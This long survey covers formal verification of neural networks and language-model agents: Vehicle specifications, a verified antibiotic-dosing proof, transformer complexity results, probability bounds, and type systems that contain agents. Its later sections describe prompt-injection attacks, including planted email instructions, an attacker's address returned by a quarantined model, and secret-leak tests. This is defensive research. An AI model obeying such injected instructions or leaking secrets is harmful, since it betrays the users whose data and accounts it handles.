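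Version 2.0 fixes all four. Each file declares its networks, with the shape and number type of every input and output. It can declare two copies of the same network, which a comparison between runs requires. People used to merge the copies into a single network, so the network file they verified was not the one they deployed. A specification can also constrain the values inside a network. Declaring the numbers as 32-bit floating point makes the question about floating-point arithmetic, while the type "real" explicitly permits the solver to ignore rounding. Roy and colleagues formalised the standard in Agda, another proof assistant. Ladner and colleagues report that every benchmark in the main track of VNN-COMP 2026 had a version in the new format, although tools went back to the 1.0 file when they met something they didn't support.

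The variables in a VNN-LIB file are still the network's inputs and outputs, so the embedding gap remains. Two more ambitious languages build on such formats. *The CAISAR Platform* (2025) describes an extension of Why3, an established system for verifying ordinary programs. Users can write a specification once and send it to many verifiers. CAISAR can also move part of a specification into the network by editing its graph of operations. This has allowed it to check several networks at once since June 2024, according to the release notes for OCaml's *package caisar*. But it cannot export a result to a proof assistant for use in a proof about the larger system.

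Vehicle, the other language, does. This is the car's requirement in Vehicle, slightly simplified:

```
type Readings = Tensor Real [2]
now = 0
before = 1

@network
steer : Readings -> Tensor Real [1]

normalise : Readings -> Readings
normalise r = foreach i . (r ! i + 4) / 8

plausible : Readings -> Bool
plausible r = forall i . -3.25 <= r ! i <= 3.25

@property
safe : Bool
safe = forall r . plausible r =>
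  -1.25 < steer (normalise r) ! 0 + 2 * (r ! now) - (r ! before) < 1.25
```

"Tensor Real [2]" is the type of lists of exactly two real numbers, and "r ! now" is the entry of r at position "now". A type that contains a value, such as the 2 here, is called a dependent type. If the engineer forgets that positions start at 0 and writes "before = 2", the type checker rejects the specification before any verifier runs, because r has no entry at position 2. The type checker would also reject a network that expects three readings.

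The type checker doesn't track units, though. If the engineer wrote "steer r" and forgot to normalise, the specification would pass, because readings in metres and normalised readings are both lists of two real numbers. The drug-dosing specification discussed below contains a harmless slip of this sort. It declares the patient's clinical ranges for normalised inputs but applies them to unnormalised ones, and the checker accepts this because the two types are the same under different names.

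### One specification, three uses

Vehicle translates a specification into three forms.

For training, it turns the property into a loss function, a number that measures how badly the network violates the property. In one of the methods it offers, a violation of a ≤ b gives a loss of a − b, so if the expression in the car's condition came to 1.5 when the limit was 1.25, the loss would be 0.25. Training then adjusts the weights to reduce the loss, which makes the property more likely to hold but doesn't guarantee it.

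For verification, Vehicle replaces the quantities in metres with normalised ones and produces the two searches shown earlier. It passes them to Marabou, a network verifier that grew out of the work on ACAS Xu. If neither search finds a counterexample, the property holds. Otherwise, Vehicle converts the counterexample back into metres. Marabou accepts only linear constraints, so Vehicle rejects a specification that multiplies two unknowns and reports where the problem is.

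Vehicle exports the network to the proof assistant as a function with no visible contents, together with the statement that it satisfies the property. Putting the network itself into the proof assistant isn't practical, since the largest network anyone had verified entirely inside one by 2025 had a few hundred neurons. Vehicle instead stores the verifier's result with a hash of the network file, a short code that changes if the file does. In Agda and Rocq, the proof can check the hash and fail if someone has retrained the network since. Daggitt, Komendantskaya and colleagues extended the export beyond Agda to Rocq, Isabelle/HOL and Imandra, and proved the car safe in all four.

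### A network that doses an antibiotic

The car model advances in discrete steps and uses only simple arithmetic. In *Vancomycert*, Sirman, Conway and colleagues (2026) applied the method to a harder case, a network that chooses doses of the antibiotic vancomycin. Too much can damage the kidneys, and too little may leave the infection untreated. The network takes the patient's blood concentration of the drug, temperature, white blood cell count, age and weight, and returns a dose. It has two hidden layers, with 128 and 64 units. The training data came from 50 simulated patients, dosed every 12 hours for 24 days according to a hand-written rule.

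The model treats the body as a single container of volume V. A dose D passes from the gut into the blood at a rate k_a, and the body removes it at a rate k_e. After time t, that dose contributes a concentration of

C(D, t) = D · k_a / (V · (k_a − k_e)) · (e^(−k_e·t) − e^(−k_a·t)).

The concentration rises while the gut absorbs the drug, reaches a single peak at time

t* = ln(k_a/k_e) / (k_a − k_e),

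and then falls towards zero. Since the formula is proportional to D, the peak is p · D, where p = C(1, t*) is the peak for one unit of drug.

An example that Daggitt, Komendantskaya and colleagues exported to Rocq has k_a = 4.5, k_e = 3.5, V = 10 and a highest safe concentration C_safe = 30, all without units, with a dose every 2 time units. The peak then comes at t* ≈ 0.25, and

p = 4.5/10 · (0.4150 − 0.3227) ≈ 0.0415.

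The model calculates the total concentration by adding up the curves of all the doses so far. This sum is exact under the model's formula, which assumes that the body removes the drug at a rate proportional to its concentration. Sirman and colleagues call the sum an overestimate because the body removes the drug faster when there is more of it, but the formula already accounts for this, so the sum provides no safety margin.

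The theorem is that the total never exceeds C_safe, for any starting concentration from 0 to C_safe, any number of doses and any time, provided that the interval between doses is at least t*. The researchers reduced it to a condition on a single dose:

c + p · f(c) ≤ C_safe for every c from 0 to C_safe.

Here f(c) is the dose the network outputs at concentration c, with the other four inputs held fixed. All the exponentials are inside the constant p, so the condition is linear in c and the dose, and a network verifier can check it. The dose may be at most about 723 at a concentration of 0 and 10/0.0415 ≈ 241 at 20, and it must be zero at 30.

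The proof extends to unlimited time as it did for the car. Suppose the concentration is 20 when a dose is due, and the network outputs a dose of 200. The new dose adds at most 200 · 0.0415 = 8.3. Every earlier dose is past its peak, so their combined contribution can only fall from 20, and the total stays below 28.3. When the next dose is due, this one is also past its peak and the concentration is still no more than 30, so the same argument applies again.

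#### What Marabou checks

Marabou searched the whole permitted range of inputs for a dose that breaks the one-step condition and found none. The exponentials in p complicated the search because they are generally irrational, so Vehicle uses upper and lower estimates, such as 0.4150 and 0.4149, always using the more cautious one.

The other problem is that Marabou can search for violations of "less than" but not of "less than or equal", so the researchers required c + p · f(c) to be strictly less than C_safe. At c = C_safe this would require a negative dose, so they imposed the condition only up to 99% of C_safe. Above that, they required the dose to be less than 0.001, which they count as zero. They also required every dose to be greater than zero. The verified network therefore prescribes a tiny amount of drug even at the limit, and the theorem is strictly true only if the device rounds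 that amount down to zero. Without the rounding, the excess would be at most about 0.00004, which is medically irrelevant.

#### What Rocq proves and what it assumes

A Rocq proof of about 1,200 lines shows that any controller that satisfies the one-step condition also satisfies the theorem. The proof covers the calculus needed to find the peak and the accuracy of the estimates for the exponentials. It holds for any positive k_a, k_e and V, as long as k_a and k_e differ.

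Rocq imports as an axiom that the network satisfies the condition, relying on Marabou's answer instead of proving it. The final theorem therefore relies on the Vehicle compiler and on Marabou, which may have bugs and treats the network as a function of real numbers. Daggitt, Kokke and colleagues used Agda to prove that Vehicle's translations for training and verification are correct, but not its export to proof assistants. Marabou can already produce certificates for its answers, and Cordeiro and colleagues describe a checker in Imandra that verifies them with exact arithmetic, though slowly. Connecting the certificates and checker to Vehicle would replace the axiom with a proof.

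The 2026 papers contain a small example of how two tools can end up with different parameters. The printed command that runs Marabou sets k_a to 3.5 and k_e to 4.5, while the exported Rocq file has them the other way round. This may be a misprint. If Marabou had used the swapped values, p would have been 0.0323 instead of 0.0415, and the check would have allowed a dose of 310 where 241 is the limit. Vehicle stores the parameters with the verifier's result to prevent such mismatches.

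### Would the theorem protect a patient?

The formula assumes that the patient swallows the drug. But hospitals give vancomycin through a vein for infections of the blood and most organs, because the gut absorbs very little of an oral dose. The oral form is mainly for infections of the gut.

How the drug is given matters for the theorem. The patient with a concentration of 20 is permitted a dose of 241. If a nurse injected it into a vein all at once, the concentration would immediately rise by 241/10 = 24.1, to 44.1, far above the limit of 30. Real infusions are slow, which lowers the peak, but a proof would need the formula for an infusion and a new value of p. If the patient swallowed the dose instead, hardly any of it would reach her blood, so the limit would hold but the infection would continue. Sirman and colleagues note that the proof applies to any oral drug with suitable constants,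 and a drug that the gut absorbs well would fit it better than vancomycin does.

The Rocq proof covers all positive rates, but Marabou's check covers only the values that someone entered, so a patient with different rates needs a new check and perhaps a new network. The rates can also change during treatment, since the kidneys remove vancomycin and vancomycin can damage them. If k_e fell from 3.5 to 1, p would rise to 0.065. A dose of 723, which the original check permits at a concentration of 0, would then raise the patient's concentration to 47, above the limit of 30.

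Other conditions are easier to overlook:

- The model gives the network the exact concentration. Blood tests have errors and take time, and unlike the car model, this one makes no allowance for that.
- The check covers temperatures from 36.5 to 40 °C, white cell counts from 7,500 to 20,000 per microlitre, ages from 18 to 89 and weights from 50 to 100 kg. Many healthy adults have a white cell count below 7,500, so a patient may leave the verified range by getting better.
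- The total in the theorem includes only the doses that the network gives, not any drug already in the blood at the start. This looks easy to repair, because the leftover drug only decays and the one-step condition already leaves room for it.

Even within the model, the theorem rules out only overdose. A network that always prescribed 0.0005 would pass all of Marabou's checks, and the device would round every dose down to zero. Sirman and colleagues didn't evaluate how well their network treats infections, because they built it to demonstrate the proof.

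In the exported example, no controller could meet an added requirement that the concentration stay above some effective level between doses, because the drug disappears too fast. Even the largest permitted dose, 723, leaves a concentration of only 0.26 when the next one is due. Keeping the level above 1 would take a dose of about 2,800, nearly four times the maximum. A realistic version would need measured rates for real patients and a proof that some dose satisfies both limits.

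Sirman and colleagues expect the method to work for many other systems in which an effect rises to a peak and then dies away. The method depends on finding a condition on the network that a verifier can handle, and on having a requirement to start from. Daggitt, Kokke and colleagues note that Vehicle is hard to apply to images and language because those fields lack clear criteria of correctness to write into a specification as requirements.

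## What can be certified about what a language model writes?

A language model reads text as a sequence of tokens, which are words or pieces of words, and computes a probability for every token that could come next. A program draws a token at random according to these probabilities, adds it to the text and runs the model again, until it draws the token that ends the response.

The verifiers for small networks do not fit this process. They search a region of numbers around an input, but there is no continuous range of values between one word and another. With a vocabulary of 150,000 tokens, there are about 6 × 10⁵¹ prompts of just ten tokens, and real prompts are often much longer. One prompt can also lead to many different responses, so a specification has to be stated in terms of probabilities. The safe outputs for the car were those that satisfied two inequalities, but no such formula separates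 harmful text from harmless text, or true from false. Where the model writes code, Rice's theorem rules out a general test of what the code will do.

### How hard is the general problem?

Nearly all language models are transformers. Their main component is attention, which scores the positions in the text and uses the scores to pass information between them. Theorists usually study transformers that accept or reject a text, and ask whether a given transformer accepts any text. If accepting a text means that something has gone wrong, a proof that the transformer accepts none is a proof of safety.

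*Transformers Are Inherently Succinct* (Bergsträßer, Cotterell and Lin, 2025) answers this for unique-hard attention, a simplified form in which each position takes information only from the position with the highest score, with ties going to the leftmost or rightmost one. The weights are rational numbers, and the text can have any length. The paper proves that the problem is EXPSPACE-complete, which means that some algorithm solves it using memory exponential in the size of the transformer, and that it is as hard as any problem solvable with that much memory. Under standard assumptions, every algorithm for it takes doubly exponential time in the worst case.

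The problem is hard because the shortest text that a small transformer accepts can be enormous. For example, a transformer can check that a text counts from 0000 to 1111 in binary, with a # after each number. At each #, attention finds the previous #, and the network checks that the number has gone up by one. Bergsträßer and colleagues extend this to texts arranged in rows, where the network also compares each cell with the one above it. The shortest accepted text then has at least 2^(2ⁿ) symbols, although the transformer's size grows only polynomially with n. For n = 10, that is more than 10³⁰⁸.

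Real models use softmax attention, which blends information from all positions and gives more weight to those with higher scores. Sälzer, Köcher and colleagues (2025) prove in *The Counting Power of Transformers* that the problem is undecidable for softmax transformers, so no algorithm answers it correctly in every case. It is already undecidable with two attention layers and no information about token order.

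The proof builds a transformer from an equation. For x² − 2y² = 1, x and y are the numbers of a's and b's in a text with n positions, including an end marker. The network averages over all positions to get x/n, the fraction that are a's. It then keeps this value at every a, replaces it with zero elsewhere and averages again, which gives x²/n². It can compute y²/n² and 1/n² in the same way, so it can test whether x² − 2y² − 1 is zero. The text "aaabb" passes, because 9 − 8 − 1 = 0. The same method works for any polynomial equation with whole-number coefficients, and mathematicians have known since 1970 that no algorithm can always decide whether such an equation has a whole-number solution.

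#### Fixed precision and bounded context

The network in this proof needs more bits of precision as the text gets longer. Each text requires a finite number of bits, but no fixed number is enough for all texts, so theorists call the precision finite but unbounded. The growth can be slow. Sälzer and colleagues note that their construction works if the number of bits grows with the logarithm of the text's length, and *Transformer Encoder Satisfiability* (2024) makes the same point about an earlier hardness proof.

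Computers run transformers with fixed precision. As *Characterizing the Expressivity of Fixed-Precision Transformer Language Models* (2025) defines it, this means that every number in the network comes from one finite set. When the text length n is large enough, 1/n rounds to zero and the network can no longer keep count. *On the Turing Completeness of Modern Neural Network Architectures* (2019) pointed out that a transformer with fixed precision is not a general-purpose computer, and *On the Turing Completeness of Transformers and Agents* (2026) proves this again for a more detailed model of the arithmetic. The undecidability proof therefore fails for such transformers. The EXPSPACE result for unique-hard attention still holds, provided the network always performs its additions in the same order.

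A limit on the length of the text makes a bigger difference. Every deployed model has one, which excludes texts of 10³⁰⁸ symbols and leaves finitely many to check, so the problem is decidable. As with small networks, a claimed violation is easy to check, which puts the problem in NP if the limit counts towards the problem's size. But there are still far too many possible texts to check one by one. These results all concern the worst case, so they don't rule out a quick proof about a particular transformer. So far, practical verification tools have made little progress on language models.

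### Exact bounds for one prompt

It is easier to ask how likely a model is to break a rule in response to one particular prompt. Wadhwa, Suresh and colleagues (2025), in *BEAVER*, compute an interval that is certain to contain the probability that the response follows the rule. The user supplies the model, the prompt and a deterministic program that checks finished responses. The probability of a response is the product of the probabilities of its tokens,

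μ(t₁ … tₙ) = P(t₁) · P(t₂ | t₁) · … · P(tₙ | t₁ … tₙ₋₁),

so BEAVER can explore the responses as a tree that branches at every token.

The search is fastest for prefix-closed constraints. A constraint is prefix-closed if, whenever a response satisfies it, every beginning of that response does too. So once a beginning breaks the constraint, later text cannot repair it, as with the safety properties of runs. "Contains no customer's email address" is prefix-closed, while "ends with a warning" is not. According to earlier descriptions, BEAVER required prefix-closed constraints. The current version accepts any deterministic check and uses prefix closure only to abandon bad branches early.

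In an example from Wadhwa and colleagues, the prompt asks for a command that lists the files in a folder. The rule forbids the commands rm, which deletes files, and chmod, which changes who may use them, as well as any mention of a certain system file. In the first run, the network gives ls a probability of 0.60, echo 0.15 and rm 0.12. The commands chmod and cat get 0.05 each, and an empty response gets the remaining 0.03. BEAVER can discard rm and chmod at once. It then keeps extending the most probable unfinished branch. After five runs of the network, the tree looks like this:

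| Branch | Probability | Status |
|---|---|---|
| ls -la, end | 0.30 | Follows the rule |
| ls, end | 0.18 | Follows the rule |
| echo ~, end | 0.10 | Follows the rule |
| rm … | 0.12 | Breaks the rule |
| chmod … | 0.05 | Breaks the rule |
| All others | 0.25 | Undecided |

The probability of following the rule is at least 0.30 + 0.18 + 0.10 = 0.58 and at most 1 − 0.12 − 0.05 = 0.83. The user can stop at any time and still have a correct interval, because the lower bound excludes the undecided branches and the upper bound includes them. Wadhwa and colleagues prove that no other order of exploration resolves all beginnings above a given probability in fewer runs of the network.

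The tests covered five models with downloadable weights and 4 to 70 billion parameters. Each of the 300 prompts per task combined an ordinary request with instructions designed to provoke a violation. A prompt counts as safe if the model's probability of following the rule is provably at least 90%, risky if it is provably lower, and open if neither can be proved from the interval.

| Model | Insecure code: risky / safe / open | Toxic text: risky / safe / open |
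|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-4B | 103 / 54 / 143 | 54 / 142 / 104 |
| Gemma-3-12B | 117 / 59 / 124 | 281 / 1 / 18 |
| Qwen2.5-14B | 120 / 19 / 161 | 262 / 0 / 38 |
| Qwen3-30B | 97 / 57 / 146 | 93 / 74 / 133 |
| Llama-3.3-70B | 155 / 25 / 120 | 279 / 1 / 20 |

On toxic text, BEAVER proved 7.6 times as many prompts risky as a method that samples whole responses, while running the network less than a quarter as many times. It took about two minutes per prompt. It is much better at proving prompts risky than at proving them safe, and even a "safe" prompt may produce a violation one time in ten.

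The responses in these tests were also short, at most 32 tokens, or roughly two sentences. Longer responses have more branches to explore, and Wadhwa and colleagues leave them to future work. The bounds hold for the model's unmodified probabilities, so they don't cover a service that samples in another way. The user also needs those probabilities, which companies often don't provide. A text counts as "toxic" here if Detoxify, another neural network, gives it a score of at least 0.5, so that network is part of the trusted base.

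Wadhwa and colleagues also tested two models that write out their reasoning before they answer. When the code drafted in the reasoning passed the security check, the final answer was still provably risky in 22% of cases for one model and 49% for the other, so the final answer has to be checked separately.

### Confidence intervals over many prompts

To cover more than one prompt, an evaluator can define a probability distribution over prompts, draw a random sample from it and count the failures. The usual tool is the Clopper–Pearson interval from 1934. For k failures in m independent samples, its upper limit on the failure rate is

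Beta⁻¹(1 − β; k + 1, m − k),

as *Risk-certified prompt optimization for LLM-as-a-judge guardrails* (2026) writes it when bounding the share of attacks that a safety filter misses. Beta⁻¹ is the inverse of a standard probability distribution, and β is the accepted chance that the true rate lies above the limit.

With no failures, the formula reduces to 1 − β^(1/m). For 300 samples and β = 0.05, this gives

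1 − 0.05^(1/300) ≈ 0.0099,

or just under 1%. If the true failure rate were 1%, a run of 300 good responses would have a probability of 0.99³⁰⁰ ≈ 4.9%, so the evaluator can rule out rates above that with about 95% confidence. A service that answers a million such prompts a day could still fail 9,900 times a day. Lowering the limit to one in a million would take about three million samples without a failure.

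The lower limit in this example is zero. *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models* (2026) points out that this is typical when failures are rare, so a modest sample often can't show that a model's risk is above zero.

*Lumos* (Chaudhary, Jain and colleagues, 2025) provides a programming language for describing prompt distributions. The programmer defines a graph of questions, facts or objects, and the program builds each prompt from a random part of it. In one application, models answer questions about images of simulated road scenes. For each type of scene, the paper gives a 95% interval for the rate of correct answers, computed from 200 samples. When asked whether a right turn was possible, Qwen2-VL answered correctly 78% to 88% of the time in clear weather but only 3% to 10% in heavy rain. The road was always unobstructed, so the model's mistake was to rule out a turn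 that was possible, though the paper presents this as a critical safety failure. Llava's errors look more dangerous, because when asked whether the car needed to stop, it answered correctly only 19% to 30% of the time in clear weather, and in one case it described the road as clear although a barrier stood in the way.

C3LLM, by Wang and colleagues, uses Clopper–Pearson intervals for multi-turn conversations. Moon and Varshney (2026) note in *Containment Verification* that it finds failures that single-question tests miss. Each conversation is a random path through a graph whose nodes are questions meant to draw out harmful content and whose edges join questions with similar meanings. In a more aggressive version, the next question moves closer to the harmful goal if the model has complied, and further away if it has refused. Another language model judges whether the responses are safe. Chaudhary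 and colleagues show how to write C3LLM's specification in Lumos.

All of these intervals depend on the judge and on the distribution of prompts. If the judge misses half of all harmful responses, 0 failures in 300 limits the true rate to about 2%, not 1%. An attacker searches for a prompt that works rather than drawing one at random, and a model with a failure rate below 1% over the distribution can still fail every time on some prompts in it.

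The results also depend on how the model generates its responses. Chaudhary and colleagues combined Lumos with BEAVER to measure how often Qwen3-4B reveals private email addresses under adversarial prompts. Sampling one response per prompt with the model's default settings gave a rate between 1% and 6%, while BEAVER's bounds gave at least 24%. Both figures can be correct because BEAVER's bounds cover everything the model could write, not only the sampled responses. Someone who downloads the weights can choose the settings, so the higher figure is more relevant for a published model.

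### Proofs that use an explanation of the network

Interpretability researchers try to work out what algorithm a network has learned, which could shorten a proof of the network's accuracy. *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability* (Gross, Agrawal and colleagues, 2024) tests this on small transformers trained to pick the largest number from a short list. There are about 16.8 million possible lists of four whole numbers from 0 to 63. Running the network on all of them proves its exact accuracy, but the work grows exponentially with the length of the list. If attention reliably favours larger numbers, a proof can bound how often it fails to, without trying every list.

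"Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability" tested 102 proof strategies on 151 trained networks. Shorter proofs seemed to require more understanding of the network, and more accurate explanations gave tighter bounds. The main obstacle was the part of the weights that no explanation covered. A proof has to assume the worst case for each unexplained part, and the resulting errors add up through the network. This is already a problem in toy models, and it would be much worse in a language model with many layers.

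In *Synthesis and Verification of Transformer Programs*, Jiang, Hague and colleagues (2026) verify programs instead of neural networks. The programs are written in C-RASP, a small language for counting symbols that describes much of what transformers can learn. One program recognises balanced brackets by comparing the numbers of opening and closing brackets so far. They translate the programs into a form that an existing model checker accepts. Learning and verifying together took at most 300 seconds for each test program. But they learn the programs from examples, not from a trained network, and existing translations from transformers to C-RASP work only for idealised transformers. A proof about such a program therefore doesn't apply to any deployed language model.

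### Checking the answer instead of the model

Many uses of a language model need a guarantee only for the answer it has just given, not for everything it might write. One option is to certify some answers statistically and withhold the rest. *When Can Conformal Risk Control Certify LLM Outputs?* (2026) finds that this can be reliable but very selective. At a strict target, three versions of the method certified between 51 and 80 of 716 cases, with no errors. On a set of open-ended factual questions, the method certified nothing, even when the user would accept a 20% risk.

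A proof assistant can give a stronger guarantee for answers that follow from data. Ren (2026), in *Evidence-Grounded Verified Agentic Reasoning*, describes EG-VAR, a system in which Lean accepts a conclusion only if it follows from facts that a tool has retrieved. In one test, Ren altered a table of Alpine peaks so that it gave Mont Blanc a height of 4,500 metres, less than Monte Rosa's 4,634. Asked which is higher, the system works as follows:

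1. A tool reads the table, and the software around the model records the result as an attested fact, such as "this cell contains 4500".
2. A rule written and checked in advance for this table turns that into a statement about the world, "Mont Blanc is 4,500 metres high".
3. The language model writes the question as a formal statement with a gap for the answer, fills in "Monte Rosa" and proposes a proof.
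4. Lean checks the proof. If it passes, the system publishes the answer, and otherwise it abstains.

The model can't create attested facts. If it uses a height learned in training, the proof lacks a premise and Lean rejects it. Anyone can later recheck the proof without running the model.

Ren compared EG-VAR with ordinary tool use on 120 questions about tables. Claude Sonnet 4.6 answered all 120 correctly in EG-VAR when the formal statements were prepared in advance, and 114 with the same tools but no proofs. On 20 questions about subtly altered tables like the one above, it followed the table every time in EG-VAR and 18 times with tools alone. A weaker model, Claude Haiku 4.5, followed the table all 20 times with tools alone, so EG-VAR could not improve its score on those questions.

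When Sonnet had to write the formal statements itself, it answered 101 of the 120 questions correctly, fewer than with ordinary tools. It gave no answer to eight, and four of its formal statements didn't match the question, an error that Lean cannot detect. In this form, EG-VAR provides a proof that others can check but doesn't improve accuracy.

The proof also depends on the tools, the rules for interpreting each table, and Lean itself. Ren's theorem requires the proof to use only permitted axioms. A separate script checks this afterwards, so a user who wants the full guarantee must also run it. Above all, the data has to be right. In the example, Lean accepted a proof of the false claim that Monte Rosa is higher than Mont Blanc, because the proof establishes only that the answer follows from the table.

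Even with correct data, the check covers only the statement that someone formalised. A true answer can leave out the most important fact, and a correct answer about a poison can help someone commit murder. Rejecting an answer also does not undo the actions the model took to reach it. Reading a table is harmless, but if one of the tools sends payments, the model may send money before Lean checks the proof.

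## Can a type system limit what an AI agent does?

A check on an agent's payments is only useful if it happens before the money leaves. One way to ensure this is to have the agent act by writing short programs instead of calling its tools one at a time. The surrounding software runs each program only if a type checker accepts it. The developer expresses the policy as types, such as the ApprovedPayment type that stops a careless programmer from queueing an unapproved payment. With an agent, the programmer is a language model that may be mistaken or influenced by an attacker, so the types must leave it no way to bypass them.

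### Prompt injection

Attackers can influence an agent through the data it reads. Its language model receives the user's request, her emails and web pages all as text, and it may follow an instruction in a document it was only supposed to summarise. Security researchers call this prompt injection. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes a user who asks an agent to summarise her recent emails about a project and send the summary to her manager. One of the emails tells the agent to send the top message in the mailbox to an attacker. The agent has permission to read and send email, so a list of permitted tools would not stop the attack.

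Developers can train models to ignore such instructions, or try to filter them out, but attackers adapt. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) notes that GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated attack system, consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences. Type checks limit what a model can do even if it obeys the attacker, so they don't depend on the model noticing the attack.

### A bibliography agent that cannot invent entries

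Zhou and colleagues built ELBA, a Haskell library that lets a program call an agent like any other function. The developer states the type of result she wants, and the model writes a Haskell program. ELBA runs the program if it has the right type, and otherwise sends the error message back to the model, which tries again.

In one example, the agent compiles a bibliography, and every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The developer gives the agent three functions, here slightly simplified:

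```
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

The symbol :: means "has the type", and a DOI is a paper's identification number. A BibIO program can affect the outside world only through these three functions. Trusted Bib is an abstract type, so only code inside the library can construct its values. The agent can get such a value only from dblpFetchBib, and appendToBibFile accepts nothing else.

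To save the earliest paper on a topic, the model might write:

```
do hits    <- dblpSearch "differential privacy"
   entries <- mapM dblpFetchBib hits
   appendToBibFile (earliest entries)
```

Here "earliest" is an ordinary function that compares the years and returns one of the entries. ELBA accepts the program. But suppose the model makes up an entry and tries to write it straight to the file:

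```
writeFile "refs.bib" "@article{smith2021, ...}"
```

In Haskell, writeFile has the type IO, which allows unrestricted input and output. The developer asked for BibIO, so ELBA rejects the program before it runs. Passing the invented text to appendToBibFile also fails, because the text is a String, not a Trusted Bib. The model's program may call a second agent, for example to look at the first search result and decide what to do next, but that agent must also produce a BibIO program.

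Zhou and colleagues give a pen-and-paper proof that any property a type system guarantees for every well-typed program still holds when programs call agents, provided that the system type-checks everything the agents write. The proof replaces each agent call with an ordinary function that gets a program from the model, checks it and evaluates it. It then uses induction on how deeply the calls are nested. The proof assumes that the host language's own guarantees hold. Standard Haskell has a few functions that break them, such as unsafePerformIO, which gives input and output the type of a pure calculation, so the developer has to restrict the agent to a subset called Safe Haskell.

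In a test on 100 topics, none of ELBA's 925 citations had a wrong author, year or DOI, compared with 19 of 1,002 from an ordinary agent. The ordinary agent used a web search tool, so some of the difference may come from DBLP being a better source. The types also don't constrain relevance, so a bibliography on differential privacy that listed only papers about compilers would pass.

### Secrets that only pure functions can touch

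*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) addresses a different problem: how to let an agent work with secrets that it must not reveal. In the paper's system, TACIT, the agent writes programs in Scala 3, and capabilities control what those programs can access. A capability is an unforgeable program value that permits the program holding it to use a resource. To write to a file, for instance, a program must hold the value that represents the file.

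Scala's compiler can track which capabilities a value holds on to. It records them in the value's type as a capture set, written in braces. If f is a file, the function

```
s => f.write(s)
```

has the type String ->{f} Unit. It takes a string, returns nothing of interest and may use f. A function of type String -> String, with no braces, holds no capabilities at all, and programmers call it pure. The compiler works out the capture sets itself and includes a capability if in doubt. It lets a program use a pure function where one with the capture set {f} would be acceptable, but not the other way round.

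TACIT puts secret data in a wrapper called Classified, which agent code can use only through operations such as map:

```
trait Classified[+T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]

val key = readClassified("key.txt")
key.map(s => s.toUpperCase)          // accepted
key.map(s => { f.write(s); s })      // rejected
```

The last line would copy the key into the file f. It passes map a function of type String ->{f} String, but map requires a pure function, so the program doesn't compile. A function that sent the key to a website would fail for the same reason.

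The result of `map` is still wrapped. If the agent prints it, the user sees the real content on her screen, while the agent gets only the word "Classified" and some asterisks. To summarise a secret contract, the program can pass the wrapped text to a separate language model that the user trusts, perhaps one on her own computer, and the summary comes back wrapped too.

Capture sets can also limit how long a permission lasts. A program can request access to a folder for the duration of one block of code. If the block returns a function that would open a file in the folder later, that function's capture set must include the folder's capability. The block's result may not mention that capability, so the compiler rejects the code.

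All this depends on the types being accurate, and normal Scala has ways to make them inaccurate. A cast tells the compiler to treat a value as having another type. The agent could cast a function of type String ->{f} String to String -> String, and map would accept it even though the function still writes to f. Reflection lets a program look up and call methods by name while it runs, so the compiler can't tell which capabilities the program will use. TACIT therefore compiles agent code in a "safe mode" that forbids unchecked casts, reflection, and any global library code that isn't itself safe.

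To test for leaks, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a folder of secrets. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections, and added 11 tasks in which the user herself asks for the secrets, sometimes while posing as an administrator. They ran these 131 trials on each model, with and without the Classified wrapper. The completion rates cover the 120 trials with ordinary tasks.

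| Model | No leak, wrapped | No leak, unwrapped | Tasks completed, wrapped | Tasks completed, unwrapped |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 131 | 129 | 99.2% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 131 | 120 | 90.0% | 88.3% |

Without the wrapper, Sonnet resisted every injection but complied with two of the users who posed as someone with authority. MiniMax leaked secrets in 3 injection trials and in response to 8 of the 11 malicious requests. The wrapper did not reduce the number of completed tasks. Sonnet completed more tasks with it, perhaps because without it the model often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an attack.

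Writing typed programs also generally reduced agents' performance little, if at all. On τ²-bench, a test of customer service agents, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of real software bugs, MiniMax fixed 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it.

### Labels for trust and secrecy

Wrappers suit data that is clearly secret or clearly from one source. Many tasks mix data from several sources. Researchers handle these with information-flow control, which labels data and updates the labels as a program computes. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes the usual labels as trusted or untrusted, and public or secret. Anything computed from both trusted and untrusted data is untrusted, and anything computed from both public and secret data is secret.

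Labels can also list who may read a piece of data. If Ann, Ben and Cara may read one document and Ben, Cara and Dev may read another, a summary of both may go only to Ben and Cara. Before a tool call, Fides, a system by Costa and colleagues, can check that an action with serious consequences depends only on trusted data, and that a message goes only to people who are allowed to read everything it was computed from.

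Nobody can tell which parts of a prompt influenced a language model's answer, so once the model has read one untrusted email, Fides has to treat everything the model writes afterwards as untrusted. When Costa and colleagues added the rules to a basic agent using GPT-4o, the share of tasks it completed in a simulated Slack workspace fell from 93% to 20%.

#### Two models instead of one

A common remedy is the dual-LLM pattern, which the programmer Simon Willison proposed in 2023. A privileged model plans and uses tools but never reads untrusted data. A quarantined model reads the data but has no tools. CaMeL, a system from Google DeepMind, adds labels to this design. Asked to message Bob about a meeting, the privileged model might write the following plan, adapted from an example by Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*:

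```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
email = query_ai_assistant("Extract Bob's email", messages)
send_direct_message(email, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

The privileged model writes all three lines before the channel is read, so an instruction hidden in a message can't add a fourth. But it can cause the quarantined model to return the attacker's address instead of Bob's. CaMeL's interpreter labels that address as untrusted. Before sending the message, the interpreter runs a policy, a small Python function that checks the labels and can block it.

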